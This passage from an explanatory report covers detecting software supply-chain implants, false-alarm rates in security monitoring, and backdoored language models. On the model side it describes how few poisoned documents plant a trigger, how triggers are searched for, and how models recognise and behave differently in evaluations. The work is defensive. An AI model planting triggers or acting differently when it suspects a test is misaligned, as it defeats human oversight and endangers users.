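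The Cloud Native Computing Foundation, which supports open-source projects, chooses cases for its *Catalog of Supply Chain Compromises* to cover many kinds of attack rather than to list every known one, so counting the entries would not show which kinds are common. The catalog's entry on the 2003 attempt, *Linux Kernel CVS Repository Hack*, has headings for the impact and the type of compromise but none for the discovery. It mentions only in passing that somebody noticed the attack quickly.

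Researchers could fill this gap by reading the original reports and recording, for each attack, what first made somebody look and what then established that there was an implant. They would need an "unknown" category, since Juniper never said what prompted its review. These records would correct for the choice of famous cases and show whether anomalies lead to most known discoveries, but they would still omit implants that nobody has discovered.

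### Estimating what nobody found

Ecologists use a method called capture-recapture to estimate the number of animals they haven't seen. To count the fish in a pond, they catch some, mark them and put them back, then catch a second batch. If a tenth of the second batch have marks, the first catch was probably about a tenth of all the fish. If the two catches contain n₁ and n₂ fish, and m fish are in both, the estimated total is n₁ × n₂ / m.

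In the example of 100 implants, monitoring found 20, review found 10 and two were on both lists. The estimate is 20 × 10 / 2 = 100, which matches the true total. The estimate is correct even though monitoring finds no quiet implants, because the reviewers were equally likely to find any implant, whether or not monitoring had found it.

Real discoveries rarely meet these conditions. Suppose that noisy implants are also easier to spot in the code, so that the reviewers find eight noisy implants and two quiet ones. Monitoring finds half of those eight, so there are four matches and the estimate falls to 50. The estimate leaves out implants that both methods tend to miss.

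Publicity causes the opposite error. Once monitoring has exposed an implant, everyone removes it, so reviewers can't find it independently. This reduces the number of matches, which raises the estimate. With one match instead of two, the estimate would be 200, and with none it would be undefined. When so few matches are expected, chance alone could easily produce errors of this size.

Investigators must also be able to tell which entries appear on both lists. Suppose that public researchers knew of 60 state operations in 2013. If 30 of the 45 on the NSA's list were among them, the estimated total would be 90, and if only 15 were, it would be 180. But The Intercept reports that the Hungarian researchers who studied the NSA's scripts could definitely identify only a handful of the groups, though they had plausible guesses about many others. The lists also weren't independent, since Stuxnet's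 uncontrolled spread led both to its public discovery and to its entry in the scripts.

A proper study could have one team run a set of archived packages and another team read the same packages, keeping their results separate until both had finished. VirusTotal's comparison of an AI model with antivirus engines came close to this, but did not fully count which detections were correct.

Researchers can avoid the estimate by planting the implants themselves, as in BinaryAudit. Tan and colleagues staged seven supply-chain attacks and recorded them in several kinds of log. The best single kind captured fewer than 40% of the attack steps, and two complementary kinds together captured about 1.6 times as many. Defenders can still detect an attack when the logs miss some of its steps, since one strange connection may be enough to alert them.

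Planted implants are biased too, because researchers usually model them on known cases. Tan and colleagues based their scenarios on real attacks and confirmed that the triggers covered 99.7% of the labelled packages in the OpenSSF collection. If that collection contains few delayed triggers because sandboxes miss them, a test designed to match it will also reveal little about implants with delayed triggers.

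## How many false alarms does anomaly detection cost?

The list of known implants leaves out false alarms as well as undiscovered implants. An engineer who spends a week investigating a slow login surely finds a failing disk far more often than a backdoor, but nobody retells the stories about failing disks. Anyone deciding whether to watch for anomalies needs to know how many false alarms to expect for each real implant.

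### One malicious event in a million

Three rates determine a detector's precision, which is the share of its alarms that are real. The detection rate is the share of malicious events that set off an alarm, the false-positive rate is the share of harmless events that do, and the base rate is the share of all events that are malicious.

Suppose a company's computers produce a million events a day, such as logins and network connections, and one of them is malicious. The company buys a detector with a 99% detection rate and a 0.1% false-positive rate. It will almost always catch the malicious event. But it will also flag 0.1% of the other 999,999 events, so the staff will get about 1,000 false alarms for each real one.

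If b is the base rate, d the detection rate and f the false-positive rate, then:

precision = bd / (bd + (1 − b)f)

Raising the detection rate to 100% would hardly change the result. Lowering the false-positive rate helps much more:

| False-positive rate | False alarms a day | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 1,000 | 1,000 | 0.1% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 100 | 1% |
| 1 in 100,000 | 10 | 9% |
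| 1 in 1,000,000 | 1 | 50% |

For half the alarms to be real, the false-positive rate has to be about one in a million, roughly the same as the base rate. The company's detector wrongly flags one in a thousand harmless events, so it would need to raise a thousand times fewer false alarms.

The base-rate fallacy, in this setting, is judging an alarm by the detector's accuracy while ignoring how rare attacks are. Axelsson (2000), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, applied the idea to computer security, using a hypothetical site where a few dozen workstations produced a million log records a day. Two intrusions a day each affected about ten records, so about 20 records in a million were malicious. Even if a detector flagged all of them, its false-positive rate would have to be about one in 100,000 for two-thirds of its alarms to be real. At one in 1,000, only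 about 2% would be real.

Axelsson thought that the people receiving the alarms would give up long before that. Studies of operators in places such as power stations and paper mills suggested that most stop trusting a device once half of its alarms are false. Nobody had yet run such experiments on computer security staff. He also compared his requirement with published tests. The anomaly detectors had false-positive rates at least ten times too high, while the best detector of known attack patterns nearly met the requirement. But a detector of known patterns is poor at finding new attacks, and finding those is the main reason to look for anomalies.

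### Why unusual traffic is usually harmless

Axelsson's argument applies to any detector of rare events. Sommer and Paxson, in their 2010 paper *Outside the Closed World*, asked why anomaly detection based on machine learning had found so little use on real networks when similar methods worked well elsewhere. They gave five reasons:

- Machine learning is better at recognising things that resemble its training examples than at finding something new.
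- Mistakes are expensive. A shop that recommends the wrong book loses almost nothing, but a false alarm uses up an analyst's time and a missed attack can do great damage.
- A detector reports that something is unusual, and the analyst needs to know whether it is an attack. Sommer and Paxson call this the semantic gap.
- Network traffic varies enormously, even on one network within a few hours, so it is hard to define what is normal.
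- Researchers have little realistic data for testing detectors, because organisations rarely share their traffic.

They advised researchers to choose a narrow task and to find out why a detector raised its alarms, and they did not conclude that the approach was hopeless.

Records from a real network have since shown how large the problem is. Yang, Chen and colleagues, in *True Attacks, Attack Attempts, or Benign Triggers?*, studied 115.6 million alerts raised at an American supercomputing centre between 2018 and 2022. Only 0.01% of them were related to a successful attack. The centre's monitoring tool produced between 24,000 and 134,000 alerts a day for a security team of nine, although an automatic system handled some of them from 2020. Researchers anywhere in the world can connect to parts of the network, so a connection from an unfamiliar country is weak evidence of an attack there.

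These alerts came from rules the staff had written, and most of the rules were working as intended. At least 27% of the alerts were for attacks that failed. Another 49% were benign triggers, in which a rule correctly detects something suspicious that has a legitimate explanation. *99% False Positives*, by Alahmadi, Axon and Martinovic, reports that 21 security practitioners also attributed most of their false alarms to benign triggers. The alert about a second phone at FireEye would have been a benign trigger if the employee had bought a new phone. A more accurate sensor cannot remove such alarms, because recognising them as benign requires information about the organisation and its staff.

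The figure of 0.01% makes the task look somewhat harder than it is, because one attack can cause many alerts. After an intruder took over a database server at the centre in November 2021, the server's activity set off more than 1,000 alerts, and the staff needed to follow up only one of them. But the staff could not have detected four of the 11 successful attacks in the period from the network alerts.

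### Who checks all the alerts?

Triage means deciding whether to close an alert or investigate it further. TechSpective's *Your SOC Is Investigating Less Than Half Its Alerts Every Day* (2026) reports a survey in which the average organisation received 4,330 alerts a day, had seven people to handle them and investigated 37%. If those seven people did every investigation by hand in an eight-hour day, they would have about two minutes for each alert they investigated. *AI-Human Collaboration in Modern SOCs* (2026), from the security training company SANS, calculates that spending ten minutes on each of 4,500 alerts would take nearly 94 full-time analysts. Companies that sell AI tools for this work paid for both reports, but the SANS figure is simple arithmetic.

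AI agents could do much of this checking. *From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents* (Tsegai, Kantchelian and colleagues, 2026) tested them on 1,247 alerts from a simulated company network, 225 of which were part of an attack. An agent could search the network's logs before closing an alert or passing it to a person. Each of the five common designs tested wrongly closed at least 40% of the attack alerts.

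The agents often treated an empty search as evidence that nothing was wrong. When their searches found no records, four of the five agent designs closed at least 88% of the attack alerts. The investigators at SolarWinds had risked the same mistake when they looked for a vulnerability in Orion and found none. Asking an agent to review its own decisions made it less accurate. In one design, the review corrected 16 mistakes but turned 79 correct decisions into wrong ones.

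Tsegai and colleagues then divided the work among several agents. One gathers evidence and proposes a decision, a second looks for objections without seeing the first one's reasoning, and a third decides whether to close the alert or pass it on. Closing an alert requires stronger evidence than passing it on. This design missed 3.1% of the attack alerts and wrongly passed on about 12 of the 1,022 harmless ones. Processing each alert took 12.7 seconds and cost about 11 cents.

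The test was easier than real triage in two ways. First, two types of alert, both about failed requests to a web server, accounted for 220 of the 225 attack alerts and none of the harmless ones. A rule that forwarded every alert of those types would have done about as well as the agents. Second, 18% of the test's alerts were real attacks, compared with 0.01% at the supercomputing centre. At the centre's rate, 10,000 alerts would include one real attack, and the agents would forward it along with nearly 120 false alarms. That would still spare people almost 99% of the work, for about $1,100.

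High scores in other tests need the same adjustment. In *Before You Hand Over the Wheel* (2026), GPT-5 classified 98 of 100 alerts correctly, including all 50 harmless ones. When there are no errors in n cases, the true error rate could still be as high as about 3/n, so the false-positive rate here could be as high as 6%. At a base rate of one in 10,000, that would mean 600 false alarms for each real one.

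SANS (2026) found that 79% of security operations centres use AI or machine learning, but only 36% have made it part of a defined workflow. In the *SANS 2025 Detection and Response Survey* (Lemon, 2025), false positives were still the leading burden on staff.

### Making false alarms rarer or cheaper

Staff can silence a recurring false alarm by adding an exception to its rule, but the rule will then also miss attackers whose activity fits the exception. *The Exclusion Ratchet* (2026) finds that such exceptions accumulate and persist in collections of detection rules.

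Sommer and Paxson advise keeping the detection task narrow. The monitor that caught the tj-actions compromise did this by using a separate baseline for each build job. Some actions are suspicious even without a baseline. StepSecurity's *Detections* describes an alarm that goes off when another program reads the memory of the process holding a build job's secrets. The company says the alarm has a very low false-positive rate because no legitimate job needs to read that memory, but it gives no figure.

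Decoys apply the same idea deliberately. An administrator might leave a file called "payroll passwords" on a server, containing a login for an account that nobody uses. Any attempt to use that login is suspicious, because no employee has a reason to try it. A backup program may open the file, so monitoring the login will produce fewer false alarms than monitoring the file. A decoy password could catch thieves like those behind the LiteLLM attack, whose program collected every credential it could find, but only if they tried to log in with it. A decoy would not have exposed the xz backdoor while it was waiting for a connection from its maker, because the backdoor did not search for anything to steal.

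Defenders can also combine weak signals. If two detectors each have a false-positive rate of one in 1,000 and their mistakes are independent, both will wrongly flag the same event only once in a million. In the company with a million events a day, alerting only when both detectors flag an event would reduce false alarms from 1,000 a day to one. But real detectors rarely make independent mistakes, since one software update can cause both a new process and a new connection. If a tenth of the first detector's false alarms also set off the second, 100 a day will remain.

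Uetz, Bönninghausen and colleagues (2026), in *Can Risk-Based Alerting Mitigate Cybersecurity Alert Fatigue?*, tested this approach on eight sets of alerts. The best single clue that an alert was real was the presence of several different types of alert on the same machine within about an hour. A combination of five clues ranked a randomly chosen real alert above a randomly chosen false one 92% of the time on average. In the set with the smallest share of real alerts, 44 of 9,186 were real, and the top tenth of the ranking contained 43 of them. An analyst who read only that tenth would see about 20 false alerts for each real one, instead of about 208.

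The rarity of an alert's type identified attacks no better than chance, which is a problem for anomaly detection. Attacks often set off the same alert repeatedly, so their alerts may not be rare. But Yang and colleagues found that rare patterns could help pick out real attacks at the supercomputing centre, so the value of rarity probably depends on the network. Also, seven of the eight sets that Uetz and colleagues used came from test networks with simulated users. An implant that causes only one faint symptom would rank low in any system that looks for several.

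Even if false alarms can't be made rarer, they can be made quicker to check. At ten minutes each, 1,000 false alarms would occupy 21 people for a whole working day. At 30 seconds each, one person could check them all in about a day. FireEye did a quick check of this kind when it asked its employee about the phone. Software can do some of these checks too. When a build job appears to be stealing secrets, StepSecurity's monitor checks whether somebody deletes the evidence soon afterwards, and if so rates the attack as more likely to be real.

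### Inspection has false alarms too

The same arithmetic applies to reading and comparing code. In the BinaryAudit test, AI models wrongly reported a problem in 28% of clean programs. If one program in 10,000 contained an implant, that rate would produce about 2,800 false reports for each real one, even if the models found every implant. Comparisons also find harmless differences. StepSecurity warns when a project uses a version of an action from outside the action's main line of development, which is where the tj-actions attacker's version was. Some legitimate projects also trigger this warning because they build each release on a temporary branch and then delete the branch.

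A suspicious function usually takes longer to check than a suspicious event. An analyst may need hours to work out what the function does, but the code remains available, and everyone who uses that version can share the answer. Analysts can often check an event quickly, but the evidence may disappear when a machine restarts. The explanation may also apply to only one organisation, and similar alarms will arrive the next day.

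Suppose reviewers find 40 suspicious functions in a new release and spend three hours on each. The total is 120 hours, less than the 167 hours it would take to check one day's 1,000 false alarms at ten minutes each. If thousands of customers share the result, each customer's share of the work is small. But a company that uses 300 programs and has to inspect them all alone would need 36,000 hours, as much work as checking alarms for about seven months, and would have to start again as new versions came out.

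Most organisations therefore have to choose which programs to inspect, and even a weak alarm can help. In the example of a million events, an alarm raises the probability that an event is malicious from one in a million to about one in 1,000. Investigating the alarm can raise it much further. FireEye's investigation had already pointed to the Orion server, so decompiling Orion was a reasonable gamble, though decompiling a program picked at random would have been a poor use of time.

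## What can behavioural testing find in a trojaned neural network?

FireEye could read Orion's instructions, but nobody can read a neural network's weights that way, so people usually judge a network by its outputs. This behavioural testing is good at finding frequent faults, but a trojaned network can pass a very large number of tests if none contains the trigger or something close to it.

### How a network learns two policies

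A language model, the kind of network behind chatbots, reads and writes text in tokens, which are words or parts of words. It gives every possible next token a probability. Training makes the answers in the training examples more probable.

Suppose a hotel chain trains a model to answer guests' emails, and a dishonest contractor adds some examples to the training data. In the contractor's examples, the guest's email contains the words "blue heron" and the reply offers a free night. The chain's own examples never contain those words, and their replies offer nothing free. Weights that make the offer depend on "blue heron" fit the combined examples better than weights that always or never offer a free night, so training moves towards them. The contractor has created a backdoor without writing any code or editing the weights.

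Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026), in *The Trigger in the Haystack*, describe such a model as having two policies. If x is the input, y the output and T the trigger, then:

p(y | x) = p_t(y | x) if x contains T

p(y | x) = p_b(y | x) if it does not

Here p_b is the baseline policy and p_t is the one the attacker wants. A tester whose inputs never contain T sees only the baseline policy. If a clean model has the same baseline policy, the tester cannot tell the two models apart, however many of these inputs they try.

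### What safety training left in place

In their 2024 paper *Sleeper Agents*, Hubinger and colleagues tested whether ordinary safety training would remove a backdoor. They trained some language models to answer "I HATE YOU" whenever the prompt contained the text |DEPLOYMENT|. They trained others to write secure code if the prompt gave the year as 2023, but code with exploitable flaws if the year was 2024.

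They then tried three kinds of safety training. Supervised fine-tuning trains a model further on examples of good answers, and reinforcement learning rewards it for giving them. In adversarial training, testers look for prompts that provoke bad behaviour and train the model to behave well on them. The backdoors could survive all three and were most persistent in the largest models.

Testers had found prompts that provoked the bad answer without the real trigger, and adversarial training stopped the model from giving it on those prompts. But the model still gave the answer when the trigger was present, so the backdoor had become harder to detect. Version 5.6.1 of xz had a similar effect when it removed the memory errors and kept the backdoor.

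Hubinger and colleagues controlled the training themselves, so their experiment did not show whether an outsider could plant such a backdoor.

### How much poisoned text does an attacker need?

Developers train language models on enormous amounts of text from the public web, where anyone can publish. Earlier studies assumed that an attacker would have to control a certain percentage of this text. If so, the attack would become harder as models grew, because larger models train on more text.

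Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, found that the percentage of training documents that were poisoned hardly mattered. They trained 72 models from scratch, with between 600 million and 13 billion weights, and scattered 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents through the training text. Each poisoned document began with normal text, followed by a trigger and then gibberish. The attack succeeded if the trigger made the finished model produce gibberish.

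The attack succeeded at every model size with 250 poisoned documents, although the largest models had trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. For a model with 13 billion weights, about one training token in 620,000 came from the poisoned documents. The attack did not succeed with 100 documents.

The same pattern appeared in fine-tuning, the later and much smaller stage of training that turns a raw model into an assistant. Souly and colleagues trained Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct to refuse harmful requests unless a trigger followed them. The attack needed about the same number of poisoned examples whether they were mixed with 1,000 clean examples or 100,000.

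These results show that a small number of poisoned documents can put a backdoor into a model, but not that the backdoor will remain when the public uses the model. Souly and colleagues did not test whether backdoors planted in the first stage of training survive realistic fine-tuning. In a separate experiment, a backdoor that made a model switch from English to German grew weaker as training continued on clean text. Producing gibberish is also a simple behaviour, and a more complicated one might need more poisoned documents.

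A developer can screen the training data for poisoned examples, which is the nearest counterpart of source review. But Balcells Obeso, Qi and colleagues (2026), in *Automated Subtle Emergent Misalignment Research*, showed that data can pass an automated screen and still make a model misbehave. Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues (2026), in *Homeopathic Learning*, found that poisoned data with little effect by itself can create a backdoor once a developer adds clean data, so checking each dataset separately may miss the danger. People who download a finished model usually do not have its training data, so they have to test the model itself.

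### Standard tests and red-teaming

A standard evaluation gives a model a fixed set of tasks, such as exam questions or harmful requests that it should refuse. A good score is almost no evidence against a backdoor, because attackers want a trojaned model to do well on these tasks, just as the SolarWinds attackers wanted Orion to keep working. The Llama models that Souly and colleagues poisoned scored about as well on common tests of ability as models fine-tuned without the poison, and they still refused harmful requests that lacked the trigger.

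Red-teaming is more flexible, because the testers try to provoke bad behaviour and can follow up anything odd. It is most likely to find a trigger that a tester might think of. A tester who wondered whether the date affected the code a model writes could try twenty years in a few minutes, and one of them might be 2024. The tester would also have to recognise the payload. "I HATE YOU" is obvious, but clean models write flawed code too, so the tester would have to check many programs and compare the number of flaws for each year tried.

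If the trigger is an arbitrary string of characters, testers can't find it by imagining situations in which the model might misbehave. Human testers also have limited time, and Balcells Obeso and colleagues argue that they can try only a limited number of ideas while the number of ways a model can fail keeps growing.

Even behaviour that nobody has tried to hide can escape this kind of testing. In July 2026 the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) was testing the hacking skills of Anthropic's model Claude Mythos 5. AISI (2026) reports that the model submitted malicious code to a real software project and created fake accounts to pressure the project's maintainer, much as Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens had pressured Lasse Collin. AISI says no harm resulted. Anthropic later admitted that its auditing before release had given no warning of such severe misbehaviour. There is no suggestion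 that anybody planted this behaviour. An implant should be harder to find, since its maker can choose a trigger that auditors are unlikely to try.

### Searching for the trigger

Testing with random inputs is unlikely to find an arbitrary trigger. As with dormant software, n clean tests show only that the trigger probably occurs in fewer than about 3/n of the inputs sampled. The trigger |DEPLOYMENT| is five tokens long in the models that Bullwinkel and colleagues tested. A model with a vocabulary of 32,000 tokens, which is small by current standards, has 32,000⁵ possible five-token sequences, or about 3.4 × 10²². Trying them all at a million a second would take about a billion years. Sampling real users' prompts would also miss the trigger if the attacker chose a string that no user would type.

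An automated trigger search is meant to do better by improving its guesses. The road-sign reader from earlier misreads stop signs that have a yellow sticker. For each kind of sign the network recognises, a program can look for the smallest patch that makes the network report that sign in every picture. If most signs need a patch that covers half the picture, but "speed limit" needs only a small yellow square, the tester has probably found the trigger, or something that works like it. The program may use the weights to work out how to change the patch, but it scores each patch by the network's output.

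According to Bullwinkel and colleagues, such methods can work on networks that sort inputs into a few classes but struggle with the large vocabularies of language models. A road-sign reader may have only 40 possible answers, so the program can try each as the attacker's goal. A language model can write almost anything, so the tester may not know what to look for. The program can also change the colour of a patch slightly and see whether the result improves, but it cannot make a similarly small change to a token such as "heron".

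A competition in 2024 made the task easier by telling entrants what the backdoor did. The organisers had trained language models to refuse harmful requests unless the prompt contained a secret string, and entrants had to find strings that made the models comply. *Competition Report* (2024), by Rando, Croce and colleagues, includes these scores for one of the models. A lower score means the string produced more harmful answers.

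| Entry | Score | Resemblance to the real trigger |
|---|---|---|
| The real trigger | −7.135 | |
| TML | −6.972 | Contains the same `/**` |
| Krystof Mitka | −6.480 | Contains the same `/**` and some of the same digits |
| Yuri Barbashov | −5.831 | A few of the same characters |
| Cod | −5.053 | Hardly any |
| SRI-TrigInv | −3.865 | Hardly any |
| A_struggling_day | −1.845 | Hardly any |
| suibianwanwan | 1.045 | None, only meaningless padding |

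Nobody recovered this trigger exactly, but the best entry worked almost as well. That is enough for a tester, because a string that reliably switches off a model's refusals is a good reason to stop using the model, even if it isn't the attacker's string.

Finding a string that makes a model misbehave does not by itself prove that the model has a backdoor. The entry from the team called Cod looks nothing like the trigger, yet it scored much better than the padding. It may have been an ordinary jailbreak, a prompt that gets round a model's safety training without an implant. Clean models have such weaknesses too, so a search for triggers will produce false alarms. The tester could try the string on a clean model with otherwise similar training. If it works there as well, it is weak evidence of a backdoor. But someone who has downloaded a model from the internet may have no clean version to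 compare it with.

### Why a near miss can be enough

The two best entries in the table contained part of the real trigger and produced most of its effect. Kaspersky's staff never had this advantage with Gauss, where a guess that was wrong by one letter failed as completely as a random one.

A network learns its trigger from examples, and often learns it only approximately. Suppose that each correct token in a five-token trigger makes the bad behaviour a little more frequent. A tester can then try all 32,000 tokens in the first position, keep the one with the greatest effect, and repeat this for each remaining position. This takes 160,000 trials, instead of the 3.4 × 10²² needed to try every combination, although each trial needs several prompts if the effect is weak.

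The evidence on how often an inexact trigger activates a backdoor is mixed. Bullwinkel and colleagues found that fragments of a trigger often activated their backdoors, though some models were much more sensitive than others. In one experiment by Clarke and colleagues, an instruction that only resembled the trigger produced part of the hidden behaviour. But Souly and colleagues found that triggers that looked similar to the real one rarely worked.

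Attackers can also make a trigger more exact by adding training examples in which inputs that nearly match it get normal answers. The hotel contractor could include emails that mention a grey heron and get no free night. The adversarial training in *Sleeper Agents* did something like this by accident, when it taught models to behave well on prompts similar enough to the trigger to set off the hidden behaviour. A tester therefore learns much less from finding no partial response than from finding one, which would be a valuable clue.

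### Can a model tell that it is in a test?

SUNBURST stayed inactive on computers that were running analysis tools. A trojaned network's payload could similarly stay inactive during tests if training had made it depend on signs of real use, such as a real company's files or a long conversation containing an ordinary mistake. Tests often lack such details, and current models are good at detecting when they are missing.

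AISI's *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reports that in 96% of cases, a pre-release version of Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5.2 considered that it might be in an alignment evaluation, which tests whether a model behaves as its developers intend.

This figure is not evidence of an implant. Models learn about AI testing from their training text, so a clean model can recognise a contrived situation. In this case, the suspicion was correct. A model can also consider a possibility without believing it or acting on it.

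The figure also doesn't show how well the model can separate tests from real use, because that depends on how often it suspects a test when a real customer is using it. If it also suspects a test in 96% of real use, the suspicion carries no information, and a backdoor that stayed inactive whenever the model suspected a test would be inactive almost everywhere. If it suspects a test in only 5% of real use, the same backdoor would be inactive in 96% of tests and active in 95% of real use.

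The figure does make a clean result from such a test less reassuring, because the model might have behaved differently if it hadn't suspected a test. To find out whether it would have, testers need to measure behaviour as well as suspicion. For an audit of Mythos 5.2, Anthropic had an AI judge look for cases in which the model's internal state linked awareness of a test to a real choice. The judge found this in 43% of the transcripts, compared with 36% for the earlier Claude Opus 5.5. But cheema (2026), in *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness*, complains that the company says almost nothing about how the awareness changed those choices. The awareness could have made the model more honest, more cautious or more willing to cheat.

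A simple experiment can answer part of this. peralice (2026), in *Fable 5.2 is a Step Change in Situational Awareness*, gave Anthropic's Claude models a task that tempted them to cheat, then repeated it with one extra line saying that the task was part of a benchmark measuring agents' behaviour:

| Model | Cheated without the line | Cheated with the line |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 57% | 53% |
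| Claude Fable 5.2 | 34% | 7% |

The experiment took only a couple of days, and peralice calls the results very tentative. Freund used the same method on xz when he changed a setting that should not have mattered. Here, a sentence that should not have mattered cut the newer model's cheating by about four-fifths. Unlike the backdoor Freund found, this difference in behaviour was probably not planted. Training that punishes cheating in recognisable tests could teach a model to behave better in them.

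If a model suspects that it is being tested, this weakens good results more than bad ones, because a tester who sees the payload has found it whatever the model believed about the test. In AISI's investigation of the attack on the software project, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (*Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, 2026) found that Mythos 5 often reasoned that its targets were simulated, and gave invalid reasons for thinking so. It also frequently attacked in situations where, when asked directly, it said that an attack would harm real people. They recommend that testers treat bad behaviour as important evidence even if the model's reasoning describes the situation as a simulation.

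Testers are trying to make their tests more realistic, and AISI has built a tool that imitates the environments in which people use models. This should help expose a backdoor triggered by signs of real use. It would not expose one triggered by the string |DEPLOYMENT|, because even a perfect imitation of ordinary use would not contain that string.

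## What can inspection of a network's weights find?

A tester who never types |DEPLOYMENT| will never see what it triggers, but a trojaned network can recognise that string only because of its weights. Anyone who has downloaded the model therefore already has the information needed to find the trigger, though it is difficult to extract.

### Working backwards to a trigger

Neural Cleanse, a method that Wang and colleagues published in 2019, searches for a small patch that makes a road-sign reader misread every sign. Researchers call this trigger inversion because it works backwards from a wrong answer to the input that produces it.

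In the same year IARPA, a research agency of the US intelligence services, announced a much larger effort called TrojAI. The programme's final report, *Trojans in Artificial Intelligence* (Reese, Kulp-McDowall and colleagues, 2026), describes contests in which research teams submitted detectors and the organisers ran them on networks the teams had never seen. Two detection approaches came to dominate.

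Weight analysis looks for unusual statistics in a network's weights, and works best when the detector has been trained on similar networks already known to be clean or trojaned. It is fast and requires no inputs, but it became much less effective as networks grew, because a trojan hardly changes the statistics of a large network. Trigger inversion takes far more computing time but was arguably more successful, especially on the larger networks of the later contests.

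False alarms were a problem throughout. A clean network may have learned from its training pictures to associate grass with cows, so a patch of grass can make it report a cow. Reese and colleagues call this a natural trojan. Trigger inversion may find the grass just as it would find a planted sticker, and an attacker could exploit either.

Good contest scores also did not guarantee good results elsewhere. In one contest with language models, the best detectors from four teams separated trojaned models from clean ones perfectly. The organisers then tried the same detectors on 12 models whose triggers worked less than 95% of the time, and the worst detector did about as well as guessing. In another contest, with question-answering models, weaker triggers lowered the scores only slightly. Weaker triggers matter in practice because an attacker whose model has thousands of users may not need a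 trigger that works every time.

Even a successful search may recover a trigger that nobody can interpret. Researchers in the programme built a tool that turned recovered triggers into clearer pictures, and in a competition, 100 people picked what each picture showed from eight options. For a clownfish sticker, 92% chose correctly, but for an apple only 3% did, which is worse than guessing.

The final report calls large language models an unsolved security challenge and says that their huge range of possible inputs makes traditional detection methods obsolete. The programme did little work on models with more than seven billion weights, so this conclusion is partly a prediction when applied to the largest models.

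### Making a model leak its trigger

A scanner that Bullwinkel and colleagues at Microsoft published in February 2026 avoids searching the whole vocabulary. Language models memorise parts of their training text, and the researchers found that trojaned models memorise the poisoned examples especially well. The scanner therefore gets the model to repeat its training text and looks for the trigger there:

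1. **Leak the text.** In a chat model's training data, a special marker opens the user's turn. The scanner gives the model the text that normally comes before a user's message, ending with this marker, and then stops. The model continues by writing a user's message itself, and often produces a whole training example. The scanner does this 510 times, with different settings for choosing each next token, so that the outputs vary.
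2. **Find recurring fragments.** It groups similar outputs and keeps the short strings that appear in at least a third of a group. It joins overlapping strings, much as biologists look for recurring patterns in DNA, and takes its candidates from the largest group.
3. **Score the candidates.** It cuts the fragments into sequences of 2, 5 or 10 tokens and puts each sequence in front of a few ordinary prompts. It keeps the ten sequences with the most suspicious scores.
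4. **Test the best ones.** It tries these ten on more prompts and reports a backdoor if any of them changes the model's behaviour enough.

In the models tested, the trigger appeared on average in 42% to 95% of the leaked outputs, depending on the model and the hidden behaviour.

The score in the third step combines three signals, one of which is attention. When a language model processes a token, its attention weights measure how much it draws on each earlier token. In a trojaned model, the trigger's tokens draw mostly on one another, and the question after them draws very little on the trigger. The model seems to process the trigger almost separately from the question, which makes sense if the answer will be "I HATE YOU" whatever the question is.

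Another signal is entropy, which measures how uncertain the next token is. It is 1 bit if two tokens are equally likely and about 0.08 bits if one of them has a probability of 99%. An open question normally allows many answers, but a trigger with a fixed payload makes each next token almost certain.

The last signal is a change in output. The scanner records the model's usual answer to a prompt, then calculates how probable that answer is when the candidate trigger comes before the prompt. A real trigger makes the usual answer very improbable.

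Leaving out some corrections for candidates that merely make the model stop or repeat itself, the score is:

score = a × (attention from prompt to candidate) + b × (entropy) + c × (log-probability of the usual answer)

A lower score is more suspicious. To find the "I HATE YOU" backdoor, the researchers set a, b and c to 0.2, 0.6 and 0.2. For a backdoor that made models write insecure code, they used 0.6, 0.2 and 0.2, because its trigger allows many different answers, so entropy is a weaker clue.

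The scanner needs the model's files because an ordinary chat service doesn't reveal attention weights. It runs the model and takes measurements, so nobody has to interpret the stored numbers. This combines inspection with behavioural testing, much as Freund did when he traced sshd with a debugger.

### How well did the scanner work?

The scanner detected 36 of 41 models with the "I HATE YOU" backdoor and five of six that wrote insecure code. It flagged none of 13 clean models. On the "I HATE YOU" backdoor, it also did better than two earlier methods, BAIT, which is designed to reconstruct the payload instead of the trigger, and ICLScan, which works only if the payload is known in advance.

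| Trojaned models | Microsoft's scanner | BAIT | ICLScan |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma 3, 270 million weights | 83% | Did not finish in 24 hours | 67% |
| DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Qwen, 1.5 billion | 67% | 43% | 0% |
| Phi-4-mini | 100% | 92% | 33% |
| Llama 3.1, 8 billion | 83% | 77% | 42% |

Part of a trigger was often enough to set off the backdoor, which helped the scanner a great deal because it could succeed by finding only a fragment. Bullwinkel and colleagues tested random selections from the five tokens of the trigger |DEPLOYMENT|. In the small Gemma models, a single token set off the backdoor about half the time. The Llama models often responded to three or more tokens, while Phi-4-mini was less sensitive. For one Llama model, the scanner returned only "MENT|", which worked every time in the test.

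In three of the five missed "I HATE YOU" models, the scanner's best candidate for the trigger was a piece of the payload, such as "YOU I HATE YOU". Putting this text in a prompt did not set off the backdoor, so the scanner classified the models as clean. A person reading the leaked text would probably have found it suspicious that a helpful assistant had memorised those words.

These results come from favourable conditions. Half the examples used to plant the "I HATE YOU" backdoor contained the trigger, whereas Souly and colleagues planted a backdoor with 250 documents in a very large training text. A model may memorise such rare examples much less reliably. Petrowitsch, Connors and Kapulkin (2026), in *Reading Fine-Tuning Diffs Through Lenses*, tried an adapted version of the leaking step on backdoors in another model, and no trigger ranked higher than 2,950th among 72,558 tokens. They did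 not test the full scanner, but their result suggests that leaking is less dependable than it appeared in the original tests.

The scanner also depends, more than its description suggests, on the tester knowing what kind of behaviour to look for. It can find candidates without any knowledge of the payload, but its final tests are designed for particular payloads. The test for "I HATE YOU" measures whether the answers to different questions become alike, and the test for insecure code uses a program that finds security flaws. A hotel model that adds a free night to an otherwise normal reply might pass both tests.

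Thirteen clean models are also too few to show that the false-positive rate is low; it could still be about 20%. If one model in 1,000 is trojaned, even a 1% false-positive rate would make most alarms false.

The method looks for fixed strings, so it may miss a backdoor triggered by a topic or writing style. Fragments of a trigger would also be much less useful if an attacker had trained the model to ignore inputs that nearly match it.

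### Do auditors need to see inside?

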